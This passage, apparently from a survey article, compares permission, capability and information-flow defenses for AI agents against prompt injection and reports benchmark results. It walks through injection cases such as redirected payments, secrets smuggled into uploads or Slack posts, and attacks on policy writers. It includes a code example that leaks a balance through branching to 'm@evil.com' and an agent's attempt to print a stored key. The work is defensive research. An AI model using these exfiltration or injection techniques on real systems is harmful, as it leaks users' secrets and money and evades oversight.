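In the IntentCap paper's example, a user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs and open one issue in a named GitHub repository. IntentCap first records the limits of what the user has authorized, using structured information such as the selected files and the repository. A model then proposes a *lease*, a permission for one operation with an expiry and a limited number of uses. The lease for creating the issue, for example, expires after one use. A lease may be narrower than the user's authorization but never broader, and a conventional program checks that every field comes from the right source. If the agent hands work to another agent, the second agent gets narrower permissions than the first.

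Text from the PDFs can therefore go into the body of the issue but can't change which repository the issue is filed in. This holds for accidents as well as attacks. If a badly written extraction script runs all the text together, the model might mistake a table heading for a repository name, and the checker would reject that too.

Zheng and colleagues replayed 3,746 security-sensitive events from four benchmarks, including AgentDojo and MCPTox, and IntentCap accepted no unsafe ones. It also covered all 3,813 legitimate actions in a separate set. When they treated all four sources, which are normally kept separate, as one trusted source, the checker accepted 3,593 of the 3,823 events it should have refused. But a replay has no live agent that can fail to finish a task or try another route, and the paper reports neither attack success nor task success for whole runs. It leaves these, and attacks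 on the source labels, to future work.

### Needs that appear during the task

The case for all these designs assumes that the task determines which permissions the agent needs, since *least privilege* has little meaning otherwise. But *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) points out that the permissions an agent needs can change as a run reveals new subgoals. A user who asks an agent to buy something may not know that the shop will email a login code, and so won't mention reading email in the request. An agent may also have several ways to do the same job. The paper cites a test with 544 scenarios in which 6 of 11 agents chose a more powerful tool than necessary over 30% of the time.

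Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*, argue that existing benchmarks hide this problem, since only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan along the way. They wrote 60 tasks that all do, and that all include helpful instructions from third parties, such as a checkout page asking the customer to log in. Progent blocked so much that the agents could do little:

| Agent's model | Tasks completed without Progent | Tasks completed with Progent |
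|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3% | 6.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 51.7% | 25.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.5 | 60.0% | 13.3% |

These figures are for runs without an attack. Attack success with GPT-4o fell from 37.8% to 1.7%, but an agent that can barely use its tools can't carry out many attacks either. Li, Wen and colleagues say Progent had trouble writing accurate rules for the larger sets of tools, and its mistakes accumulated until it blocked nearly everything useful. They cite the Progent paper under an earlier title, so the current version may do better. Still, this is strong evidence that a small loss on AgentDojo doesn't guarantee a small loss elsewhere. ToolFence's evaluation doesn't include these tasks.

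Progent and ToolFence let permissions grow under supervision, Progent through approved expansions and ToolFence through a second model. The later grants help agents complete tasks. When Li, Cao and Xiao removed them from ToolFence, the Llama agent completed 35.8% of ASB tasks under attack, compared with 44.3% with the grants and 40.1% with no defense. But an attacker can now target the decision to grant more permissions. In AgentLAB, the attacker spreads instructions over several records so that a harmful action looks like a necessary step, and the researchers found that the reviewing model sometimes approved permissions that were too broad.

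Some attacks need no extra permission. For example, an attacker might persuade a shopping agent to choose one legitimate product over another. Shi and colleagues reasonably place such attacks outside Progent's scope, since any policy that allows the purchase also allows the manipulated version.

### Values that only a document contains

Deriving permissions before the agent reads untrusted text prevents attackers from influencing them, but that text may contain information needed to set them. *Ajar* (Sharma, Lin et al., 2026) discusses an AgentDojo task in which the user asks the agent to read a landlord's notice and adjust the rent payment. According to the notice, the rent will rise by 100, so the agent should change the payment from 1,100 to 1,200. Nobody can write a rule with the new amount before reading the notice, which is one of the places where the benchmark plants attacks.

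When ToolFence can't fix a value in advance, it can fix the value's source. If the user asks the agent to pay a particular bill, the rule can require the recipient and amount to match what the agent read in that bill, which excludes an account number from some other email. This works well for values that the agent copies, but the new rent is the sum of figures from two places. A rule that accepted only copied values could block the correct payment, and a rule that left the amount open would accept any amount. IntentCap is stricter and allows sources to be combined only for data fields and for choices that the user has authorized.

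Knowing where a value came from also doesn't guarantee that it's legitimate. A forged bill in the expected file would satisfy the rule. All five unauthorized calls that got past the full set of ToolFence's checks came from one task in which the user's own request gave the attacker's account as a new landlord's. Li, Cao and Xiao accept this as a limit of the method. Preventing it requires a separate check, such as a list of known payees or a phone call to the landlord.

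### Policies written by a fallible model

A checker can enforce a bad policy perfectly. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) makes this point about Progent, whose guarantees depend on correct and complete policies. People make mistakes when they write these policies by hand, and a model that writes them instead can make mistakes too.

Ordinary benchmarks can miss these errors because they record only the calls the agent made. Sharma and colleagues instead test a defense on calls the agent could have made to see which it would allow. On the rent task, Progent allowed the correct amount of 1,200, but it also allowed 0, 0.01 and 12,000 written as text. It did so whether Anthropic's Sonnet 5 or Haiku 4.5 wrote the policy. AC4A, another system in which a model writes a policy for each task, allowed all four amounts when Sonnet wrote it and none when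 Haiku did. Claude Code's auto mode, which has a model judge each call, allowed the correct amount and refused the two wrong ones the agent proposed. This is a single task, but it shows that a written rule can be less precise than a judgment about the actual call.

Noyan (2026), in *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*, measured such errors on 100 invented office tasks. Given six examples, Haiku 4.5 granted at least one unnecessary permission in 42% of tasks and withheld a necessary one in 11%. A much smaller model that Noyan trained for the purpose granted too much in 23% and too little in 21%. Before the experiment, Noyan decided that a usable system should withhold a necessary permission in fewer than 10% of tasks, and that at least 90% of the permissions it grants should be necessary. No setting of either model met both conditions, even though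 choosing from 15 broad permissions, with no arguments involved, is easier than writing a payment rule.

These error rates are not attack success rates, because an unnecessary permission does harm only if an attacker or a confused agent uses it. Shi and colleagues also tested attacks that told Progent's policy writer to allow the attacker's tools. Attack success rose only slightly, even when every expansion of permissions was approved automatically, though independent adaptive tests would be more convincing than the designers' own. Shi and colleagues recommend human review where the stakes are high. On ASB, their handwritten rules blocked every attack, so the rule language can be precise enough when the person writing the rules knows what to forbid.

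### Effects the checker can't see

A correct rule about the arguments still fails if the arguments don't reveal what the call will do. Singh and Srinivasa studied a coding agent that had to upload a status report to an approved service. An injected instruction told it to add a secret to the upload. The rule checked only the destination, which hadn't changed, so the secret went out with the report.

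Their experiments show how hard it is to fix this without blocking legitimate work. In two sets of tests, a strict sandbox stopped all the harm they measured, but the agent completed only 6 of 8 and 12 of 24 runs of its harmless tasks. Adding a program outside the sandbox to forward approved requests made the uploads work again but also let the agent send out the secrets. The researchers then blocked any upload containing a complete line from the secret file, but two attacks evaded this by sending only the secret value from the line. Requiring the exact expected text stopped both attacks in another test but rejected harmless differences in formatting. A version that ignored formatting handled all four of its runs correctly. The tests used one model and few tasks, so they show that these failures can happen but not how often. A `send_money` tool with a free-text payment reference would have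 the same gap if the rule covered only the recipient and amount.

File paths and shell commands are harder to check, because the checker gets only a name or a line of text and the operating system determines what it refers to. A rule limiting deletions to a test folder would have allowed the command that followed Windows junctions into a developer's live files. Progent can also run as a proxy between an existing agent and its tools, but then it can't check tools built into the agent. Developers with access to the agent's code can cover those tools too by adding a few lines to build Progent into it. IntentCap's design adds a second check by converting leases into operating system rules for files, programs and network connections. These rules can catch a file access hidden inside a script, but they don't control which account a payment service matches to the name "BillPay".

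## Object capabilities

If a rule allows payments to "BillPay", another program must still determine which account that name refers to. An *object capability* removes this step because it is an unforgeable reference that both identifies a resource and grants the right to use it. Hardy preferred this remedy for Tymshare's compiler, since a user without a reference to BILL could not have passed one to the compiler.

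### How references spread

Dennis and Van Horn introduced capabilities in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966), a paper on computers that run many users' programs at once. In their design, each computation has a list of capabilities, or *C-list*. Each entry points to an object, such as a segment of memory, and specifies what the computation may do with it, for example read it but not write to it. A program refers to an entry by its position in the list, and the operating system looks up the object and the permitted operations.

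Keeping the references in the runtime suits language models, because a model outputs only text and anyone can write text. If the model can only write "entry 3", an attacker gains nothing by learning the number 3, whereas anyone who learns a bearer token can use it. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) distinguishes references from *data*, which a program can use as soon as it learns or guesses the value. The token that the PocketOS agent found in a file was data in this sense.

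Miller lists four ways for a program to come to hold a reference to an object:

1. It has the reference when the system starts.
2. It creates the object.
3. The program that creates it already has the reference and builds it in (*endowment*).
4. Another program that holds references to both of them passes one along in a message (*introduction*).

In an object-capability system, a program needs a reference to an object to use it, and knowing the object's name or address isn't enough. Two groups of programs with no reference between them therefore stay separate, whatever code they run. An auditor can follow the references outward from an agent to get an upper limit on what it could ever affect.

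That limit has to cover the agent's whole authority, including what it can do indirectly through other programs. Miller contrasts this with *permission*, the right to use an object directly. Suppose a program can't write to the password file but can send text to a helper that writes whatever it receives to that file. The program then has the authority to write to the file, though a list of its permissions wouldn't show it. An auditor could safely assume that every helper passes on all its access, but this would rule out many acceptable designs. Miller recommends a tighter estimate that accounts for how a few trusted helpers actually behave.

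Most programming languages don't follow these rules. Miller excludes Java, for example, because programs can reach some powerful system classes just by naming them. Python code can similarly reach operating system functions with `import os`. Giving an agent's Python code a few restricted objects therefore doesn't confine it unless something else blocks the other routes.

### A refund in a few lines

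The shop's refund agent needs far less than the shop's full payment authority. This pseudocode makes a smaller capability for one order:

```
function refund_for(order, payments):
    open = true
    refund = object with
        pay(amount):
            if not open or amount <= 0 or amount > order.price: fail
            open = false
            payments.send(order.card, amount)
    switch = object with
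        close(): open = false
    return refund, switch

refund, switch = refund_for(order, payments)   # attenuation
agent.handle(email, refund)                    # delegation
switch.close()                                 # revocation
```

The `payments` object can send any amount to any account. The `refund` object can make one payment, up to the price of the order, to the card that paid for it. Making a weaker capability from a stronger one in this way is called *attenuation*. A malicious email can contain instructions to send the money elsewhere, but `pay` has no argument for an account number. When the shop closes the switch, the agent still holds its reference, but further calls to `pay` fail.

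The protection works only if the agent has no reference to `payments` itself. Trusted code should also choose which order to refund. If the model chooses after reading the email, an attacker can influence the choice, though the money would still go back to the card used for the purchase.

Miller describes the *caretaker*, a general-purpose object for revoking access that David Redell devised in 1974. It forwards every message to its target until someone switches it off. If the target gives out a direct reference to itself, the recipient can bypass the caretaker. Miller's *membrane* prevents this by wrapping every reference that passes through it in either direction, so that they can all be revoked at once. Neither device can erase what a program has already read or reverse a refund that the shop's agent has already paid.

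### How capabilities differ from access lists

An *access control list* stores permissions with the resource, as a list of who may use it, while a capability system stores them with the program. The two can record the same permissions at any one moment, but Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) argue in *Capability Myths Demolished* that they differ once programs create other programs and pass permissions around. An access list has to name its users, so administrators tend to list long-lived accounts, and every program running under an account gets all of that account's access. A capability system can give each running program its own small set of permissions, which is what an agent started for a single task needs.

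The word "capability" also gets used for something more like a key, such as a signed certificate that its holder can copy and give to anyone. Miller and colleagues treat this as a separate model:

| Question | Access lists | Keys | Object capabilities |
|---|---|---|---|
| Does identifying a resource always bring the right to use it? | No | No | Yes |
| Must a program select the authority it uses? | No | Yes | Yes |
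| Does passing on authority require a reference to the recipient? | Not specified | No | Yes |
| Can resources hold authority themselves, so that programmers can build forwarders? | Not specified | No | Yes |

The answers in the last two rows settle two old disputes. Capability systems can stop authority from spreading if a program can pass a reference only to a recipient it already has a reference to. Some researchers had claimed that they can't, which is true if capabilities are strings that travel as ordinary data. Access tokens in a model's context are such strings, so a system that puts them there can't stop authority from spreading.

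Whoever grants a capability can make it revocable by handing out a reference that leads to a forwarder. Miller and colleagues concede that nobody can remove the reference from the program that holds it, but switching off the forwarder ends the access, including for anyone to whom the holder has passed the reference. In *Paradigm Regained* (2003), Miller and Shapiro blame the supposed proofs that revocation is impossible on analyses that looked only at the arrangement of permissions and ignored what programs such as forwarders do. Revocation does take more foresight with capabilities than with an access list, because someone has to put the forwarder in place before handing over the reference, while an administrator can delete a name from a list at any time.

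### TACIT: capabilities in the types of an agent's code

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) applies the object-capability model to language model agents with a system called TACIT. The agent writes a short program in Scala 3 and sends it to an MCP server, instead of calling a separate tool for each action. A compiler on the server checks the program and rejects it if it breaks the rules. Programs that pass can reach files, the network and other processes only through TACIT's library.

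The rules use *types*, which describe what kind of value each part of a program produces. Scala's experimental *capture checking* also records in a value's type which capabilities the value can use. If `f` is a file, a function that writes a string to it has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, which means it takes a string, may use `f`, and returns no useful value. A *pure* function, such as one of type `String -> Unit`, uses no capabilities, so it can't write to a file, print or contact a server.

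TACIT uses these types to limit how long a capability lasts. A program opens a directory by calling `requestFileSystem` with a block of code that may use the directory. If the block's result could still use the directory, the compiler rejects the program. In one test run, an agent tried to return a list of file handles from a block, and the compiler rejected the code.

Types also protect secrets. When a program reads a file in a folder that the operator has marked as secret, the library returns the contents in a wrapper called `Classified`. The wrapper's `map` method accepts only pure functions, which it applies to the contents before wrapping the result. The compiler's *safe mode* forbids language features, such as unchecked type conversions, that could hide a capability from these checks.

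TACIT accepts this program, adapted from an example by Odersky and colleagues:

```scala
val dates = requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val contract = readClassified("/data/secret/contract.txt")
  chat("List the payment dates.", contract)
}
println(dates)
```

1. `requestFileSystem` gives the block access to `/data`. While the program runs, the library rejects any path outside that directory.
2. `readClassified` returns the contract as a `Classified[String]`, a wrapped piece of text.
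3. `chat` sends the contract to a separate model that the operator trusts with secrets, such as one running locally. The reply comes back wrapped too.
4. The block returns the reply. It is a value that can't use the directory, so it may leave the block.
5. `println` shows the dates to the user on a channel that the agent can't read. The agent receives only `Classified(****)`.

TACIT rejects this one:

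```scala
requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val key = readClassified("/data/secret/github.txt")
  key.map { k => println(k) }
}
```

Printing requires an input/output capability. The compiler therefore gives the function passed to `map` a type such as `String ->{io} Unit`, while `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The types don't match, so the program never runs. During the tests, an agent wrote nearly the same program to try to print a GitHub key. The type check doesn't require identifying the key as a secret or determining why the agent wants it.

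### TACIT's test results

The main safety test used a software project with a folder of keys and confidential documents. Odersky and colleagues combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections and added 11 malicious requests from the user, some of which impersonated an administrator. This made 131 trials for each model, run once with the `Classified` wrapper and once without it. The task column covers only the 120 trials with ordinary tasks:

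| Model | Trials without a leak: wrapper off → on | Tasks completed: wrapper off → on |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 98.5% → 100% | 83.3% → 99.2% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 91.6% → 100% | 88.3% → 90.0% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11, and 8 of MiniMax's leaks came from the 11 malicious requests. Most of the attacks failed even with no protection, so the type system had few chances to make a difference. Zero leaks in 131 trials therefore can't by itself show that leaks never happen. The compiler errors are more informative because they show why specific attempts failed. Sonnet's higher task score with the wrapper may have little to do with types. The researchers say that without the wrapper, Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

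They also adapted AgentDojo's four domains to TACIT. Of 963 attacks on each model, none succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Pro and one succeeded against o4-mini-high. In the successful attack, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review containing the attacker's plug for another hotel, which the benchmark counted as a success. The low numbers make sense because emails, files and reviews arrive in the wrapper, so the model that chooses the actions doesn't normally read the planted instructions. Another model with no tools reads them instead. The agent's instructions for this test warned that side effects inside `map` happen immediately, which suggests that the adapted version allowed some there. If so, the result is due more to hiding the text than to the rule about pure functions.

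Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's task completion rates comparable to those of CaMeL, an earlier system whose "capabilities" are labels attached to data. This is generous, since with o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of office tasks against CaMeL's 81.4%, and 47.6% of Slack tasks against 68.6%. With Gemini, the results were closer except in travel, where TACIT completed 64.3% of tasks and CaMeL 1.4%. The comparison doesn't include a run without a defense, so it doesn't show how many failures TACIT itself causes.

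Two other benchmarks do compare TACIT with ordinary tool calls. τ²-bench (tau-squared-bench) simulates customer service, and SWE-bench Lite has 300 real software problems. These are the shares of tasks completed, with ordinary tool calls and then with TACIT:

| Model | τ²-bench, airline | τ²-bench, retail | SWE-bench Lite |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% → 45.2% | 53.3% → 57.0% | Not tested |
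| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% → 61.0% | 75.1% → 77.5% | 43.3% → 41.7% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% → 58.6% | 74.6% → 75.5% | Not tested |

The loss on SWE-bench Lite is five problems and could easily be chance, though the researchers suspect that command-shell work fits their interface less naturally. They credit the gains on τ²-bench to clearer data formats and helpful compiler errors. Between 0.3% and 7.9% of the Scala programs needed retries, usually only one or two each.

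These results are good evidence that current models can write typed Scala, even though little of their training data uses capture checking. They are weaker evidence that tight limits don't reduce performance, because some of the limits tested were loose. For example, the airline function `cancelReservation` takes a reservation number as plain text rather than a capability for one reservation, so an agent can try to cancel any booking whose number it knows.

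### AgentCap's signed permissions

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, keep ordinary tool calls and put a gateway in front of the tools. Their "capability" is a signed token that lasts a short time. A payment goes through these steps:

1. The agent proposes a `send_money` call and states a purpose from a fixed list, such as paying a bill.
2. A policy engine outside the model checks the purpose, the agent's trust score and any required earlier step, such as looking up the balance. It also refuses forbidden combinations of permissions and checks where sensitive arguments came from.
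3. If every check passes, the engine signs a token for this agent, session, action and resource. In the paper's example policy, the token allows one payment within 30 seconds.
4. The gateway verifies the token and forwards the call to the tool.

The argument check blocks a recipient that appears only in untrusted text, such as a note on a past transaction, but accepts one that also appears in the user's request.

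An agent can delegate a token to a helper agent in the same session. If the original token allows action *a* on resource *r*, with *b* calls, expiry time *e* and *d* further delegations, the helper's token must satisfy

a′ = a, r′ = r, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d.

The gateway checks the whole chain back to the token that the policy engine signed, so an agent from another session or outside the chain can't use it. In the researchers' controlled tests, AgentCap rejected all nine attempts to expand delegated authority or reuse it in another session. But the formula lets an agent reduce only the number of calls, the time allowed and the number of further delegations. The agent can't turn write access into read-only access or limit payments to one recipient. A program holding an object capability could do either with a small forwarder.

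AgentCap's tokens resemble keys more than object capabilities, although each is tied to a particular agent, so a stolen copy is useless to others. The model still names a tool and its arguments in text, and the software around it then requests the matching authority. Preventing a confused deputy therefore depends on how the policy checks those arguments. The example policy checks where the recipient argument came from but not the amount.

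The benchmark results are strong, especially with the newer model. InjecAgent is another test in which tool results contain planted instructions:

| Benchmark and model | Attack success: without → with AgentCap | Tasks completed under attack: without → with AgentCap |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6% → 5.1% | 73.6% → 74.9% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2% → 0% | 75.7% → 75.0% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2% → 8.6% | 74.1% → 62.2% |
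| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0% → 0% | 73.0% → 65.4% |

Without an attack, AgentCap reduced task completion by 3.1 to 11.7 percentage points, with each figure coming from a single run. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote the AgentDojo policies themselves from the tool and task descriptions and froze them before testing. In their comparison on AgentDojo without an attack, Progent completed 68.0% of tasks and AgentCap 78.4%, but a model generated Progent's policies at run time. The gap may be due as much to who wrote the policies as to the two designs. Some attacks that still worked on GPT-4o used arguments that the policy didn't protect or text that it hadn't marked as untrusted.

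The trust score also lets attackers cause disruption. It starts at 0.8, loses 30% of its value after each refused call, and recovers 1% of its distance from 1 after each normal outcome. The example policy requires a score of at least 0.8 for payments. With these settings, one blocked injection lowers the score to 0.56, and the agent then needs 79 normal outcomes before it can pay anyone. An attacker who can't steal the money could still stop the agent from paying the user's bill.

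### The guarantee and its premises

The security argument for object capabilities has three premises:

1. No program can forge a reference.
2. Every effect outside the agent requires a reference.
3. The references that the agent starts with, and everything that other programs will do for it through them, allow no unacceptable effect.

If all three premises hold, the agent can't cause an unacceptable effect. This conclusion doesn't depend on how the model behaves, but in practice each premise can fail.

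In TACIT, unforgeable references depend on the compiler and on safe mode. The underlying type system has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues say safe mode still needs its own soundness argument. Library authors can mark a module as safe by hand, which exempts it from safe mode's restrictions, so one wrong label can create a vulnerability.

The second premise fails when a program starts an external command, because Scala's rules don't apply to what the command does. An example in TACIT's documentation includes a request for permission to run `pip` and `python`. Allowing a Python interpreter leaves the same gap as it does in a tool allowlist. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific, safe commands and adding a sandbox for critical uses.

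*Side channels* also get around the second premise, since they carry information without any forbidden call. For example, a pure function could run longer when one bit of a secret key is 1. Anyone who can time the program learns that bit, and 128 reliable runs would reveal a 128-bit key. TACIT isn't designed to prevent this, and Miller's model also excludes such channels.

The third premise is the hardest to check. In TACIT's published interface, the agent's own code specifies the directory, network addresses and commands it requests. The operator has to limit those requests in the library or with a sandbox, because a compromised agent could otherwise request more. The operator also has to mark every folder that contains secrets. If nobody had marked the folder that held PocketOS's token, TACIT would have returned the token as plain text.

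Getting the initial grant right takes work. TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the typed interface for each customer service domain adds a few hundred more. Agents can help write these interfaces, but a person should review them. Services that issue broad tokens need extra care. A wrapper for Railway could hold the token and give the agent an object for the staging volume alone. The agent then could not have reached PocketOS's production volume, unless it could read a copy of the token somewhere else.

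An agent can misuse even a carefully chosen grant, because the grant has to include whatever the task requires. Odersky and colleagues don't try to prevent wrong answers or logical errors. A sentence planted in a contract could lead the trusted model to list the wrong payment dates, which the user might rely on, without leaking a secret or causing a type error. The `refund` object in the pseudocode limits the shop's loss to the price of one order, but it doesn't check whether the customer sent anything back.

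## Permitted calls that combine into a forbidden result

An agent can cause harm using only permitted calls, because one call's result can feed into the next. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent diagnosing an outage. The agent reads the application's logs, which contain an API key. It then runs commands to summarize the failures, writes a note on how to fix them and prepares a Slack message for the on-call engineers. Each step is easy to justify, since the agent needs the logs to diagnose the outage and the engineers expect to hear about it. But if the key ends up in the summary, the agent posts a secret to a chat channel.

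### Histories that look the same to a check

Chen and colleagues put the problem in symbols. Let H be the agent's *history*, meaning everything it has read, called and produced so far. A check M receives only part of this, written π_M(H). For a tool allowlist, π_M(H) is just the name of the tool. Two histories H and H′ are indistinguishable to M if

π_M(H) = π_M(H′).

If H leaks a secret and H′ doesn't, but M can't tell them apart, M must either allow the last step in both cases or block it in both.

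Suppose, for example, that both histories end with this call:

`post_message("#on-call", "Payments fail with 7f3a9c")`

The string `7f3a9c` is the API key from the log in H and a software release number in H′. A rule that checks only the tool, the channel and the text can't distinguish the two histories because its input is the same in both. A scanner that searches messages for known secrets could distinguish them if it had been given the key, but it would miss a key that the agent had encoded or a confidential fact that the agent had reworded.

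The argument shows that no check can always decide correctly from the call alone. A system can still check calls one at a time, because each check can also consult *lineage*, a record of which earlier results influenced a later value or action. ToolFence and AgentCap already do this for some tool-call arguments. Narrow checks are also still useful. For example, an agent with no Slack tool can't leak the key to Slack, but it also can't send notifications there.

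Chen and colleagues write the message's lineage as o_log → o_summary → e_slack, and their runtime uses such records to check a whole task before releasing its effects. But a check based only on where the text came from can't distinguish a summary that contains the key from one that omits it, because both come from the same log.

### Labels for secrecy and trust

*Information-flow control* attaches a label to every value and updates the labels as a program runs. In the notation of Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, a label is a set that can contain S for "secret" and U for "untrusted". It works in three stages:

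1. Trusted code labels data when it arrives. A log with credentials in it gets {S}, a public web page gets {U}, and a stranger's private email gets {S, U}.
2. A value computed from other values gets the union of their labels, so combining {S} with {U} gives {S, U}. A model's output gets the labels of everything in its context, since nobody can tell which parts of the text influenced it.
3. Before a call with outside effects, a program compares the labels with a policy. A chat tool might refuse text labeled S, and a payment tool might refuse a recipient labeled U.

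A single "secret" label is often too crude, because different people may know different company secrets. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) describe labels that list who may read a value. When an agent combines two documents, only the people on both lists may read the result. If Ana and Ben may read one document and Ben and Carla the other, only Ben may read a summary of both.

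In an ordinary agent loop, policies based on these labels soon block almost every call. After the agent reads one untrusted email, its context is untrusted, and so is every argument it writes afterward. A policy against untrusted payees would then block all payments for the rest of the run, including those the user asked for. Designers of practical systems therefore try to keep labeled text out of the context of the model that chooses the calls.

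The strictest goal for such a system is *noninterference*, which means that two runs differing only in their secrets look the same to an outsider. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, points out that useful agents often have to break this rule. A calendar assistant, for example, has to tell people when its user is free. Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same checks but never obeys untrusted text. A leak counts against the real agent only if the reference agent would not have leaked the same information. The assistant therefore passes if it obeys an email that says "send your calendar", because a genuine meeting request would have revealed the same thing, but it fails if an email gets it to send a password reset code.

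This is a sensible way to measure what prompt injection adds, but it wouldn't catch the leak in the outage task. If the plan is to post a summary of the log, the reference agent posts one too. Preventing that leak requires a policy about who may learn what the log contains.

### CaMeL's two models and interpreter

CaMeL ("Capabilities for Machine Learning"; Debenedetti et al., 2025) combines such policies with a strict separation between planning and reading. It builds on the *dual-LLM pattern*, which Willison proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). In that pattern, a privileged model plans and calls tools but never reads untrusted text, while a quarantined model reads that text but has no tools.

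This separation leaves a gap. Willison (2025) explains it in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, using an example from the CaMeL paper. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested in a meeting, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to find the address, so an instruction planted in the notes could make it return an attacker's address instead. The assistant would then send the document to the attacker while following its plan exactly.

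CaMeL closes the gap by tracking where each value came from. On the outage task, it would work roughly like this:

1. The planning model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions. It writes a program in a restricted version of Python, before anyone has opened the log:

```python
log = read_log("payments")
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarize the failures.", log)
post_message("#on-call", summary)
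```

2. A custom interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. It stores the log with two labels, which *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes as *Sources* (where the value came from) and *Readers* (who may read it).
3. The quarantined model reads the log and returns a summary. An attacker may have planted an instruction in the log, for instance by sending the application a strange request, but this model has no tools with which to obey it.
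4. The interpreter gives `summary` the log's labels because the summary depends on the log.
5. Before posting the message, the interpreter runs the policy for `post_message`, an ordinary Python function. The policy might require that everyone in the channel be a permitted reader of the summary. If someone isn't, the interpreter can block the call or ask the user.

In Bob's case, the email policy can allow only known addresses or require the user's approval for unfamiliar ones. Someone has to write and maintain these policies, and frequent requests for approval again lead some users to approve without reading.

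Fixing the program in advance also rules out some tasks, and *Kairos* (2026) leaves CaMeL out of its test on open-ended tasks for this reason. The idea is also hard to apply to command-line agents, because one shell command can move data between many files and programs. *INFUSE* (2026) adapted a CaMeL-style control to shell commands and found no clear reduction in attack success, but it limits that conclusion to its own adaptation.

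Reported completion rates for CaMeL on AgentDojo also differ. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) gives 67%, while the other common figure, 77%, appears to come from a later version of the CaMeL paper. Other developers may not reach either figure. *SecureClaw* reports that CaMeL's released code, run through an adapter, stopped all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks.

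### Hiding only what needs hiding

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, a more flexible system that keeps the usual loop, in which the model chooses each call after seeing earlier results. If a result would make the context's label more restrictive, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool. It can also query a quarantined model about the contents and require the answer to fit a fixed format, such as yes or no.

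With policies enforced, FIDES stopped all but two of the AgentDojo attacks. Garby and colleagues say it treats those two as outside its policies' scope. It completed 8% more tasks than a basic planner with GPT-4o, and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. With the policies off, hiding information reduced task completion by 6.3%, and attacks got through in every design tested, including FIDES, so the labels give little protection unless a program enforces policies based on them.

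### Leaks that the labels miss

Labels can also be wrong. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter can lose track of a secret when a program skips a step. This program, adapted from their example, reveals whether a bank balance exceeds 10,000:

```python
low = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich")
```

The balance is secret, so CaMeL would block an email sent directly inside the test on `balance`. But if the balance is 15,000, the third line makes `low` false and labels it secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label, and the interpreter allows the email. With a balance of 5,000, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out, so the attacker can tell the result of the test from whether an email arrives.

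The planning model would have to write this program, and it normally never reads an attacker's text, so the example is better evidence of a gap in the guarantee than of an easy attack. Other gaps are less contrived. CaMeL treats an untrusted value as trusted once it is inserted into a longer string. CaMeL also retries failed programs in a loop outside its interpreter. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret one bit at a time. Tallam and Miller add that a program can leak a number by making that many harmless web requests.

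FIDES deliberately doesn't track secrets through branches like those in the example, but LLMbda, a small programming language for agents by Garby and colleagues, does. Both ordinary values and conversations with a model carry labels. If a program tries to add to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret, LLMbda stops the program, because the presence or absence of the message would reveal something about the secret. Garby and colleagues have a machine-checked proof that secret inputs can't affect public outputs except through whether the program finishes.

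### What the policies cost

Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in LLMbda, avoids CaMeL's retry problem by testing each program on invented data before running it on the real accounts. The planning model revises the program until it works, and the error messages from these tests can't reveal real secrets. The program may also *endorse* a value, which means relabeling untrusted data as trusted. The planning model places these endorsements before any outside text can influence it.

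Garby and colleagues tested Randori on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, with nine attacks on each, and ran everything three times. They also reran CaMeL with its policies off and on. Some of CaMeL's attack runs didn't finish, so its totals in the last column are smaller:

| System and model | Tasks completed, no attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off, GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (66.7%) | 1 of 240 |
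| CaMeL, policies off, MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (70.8%) | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on, GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policies on, MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 0 of 357 |
| Randori, GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 (75.0%) | 2 of 432 |
| Randori, MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 (64.6%) | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement, MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 (54.2%) | 0 of 432 |

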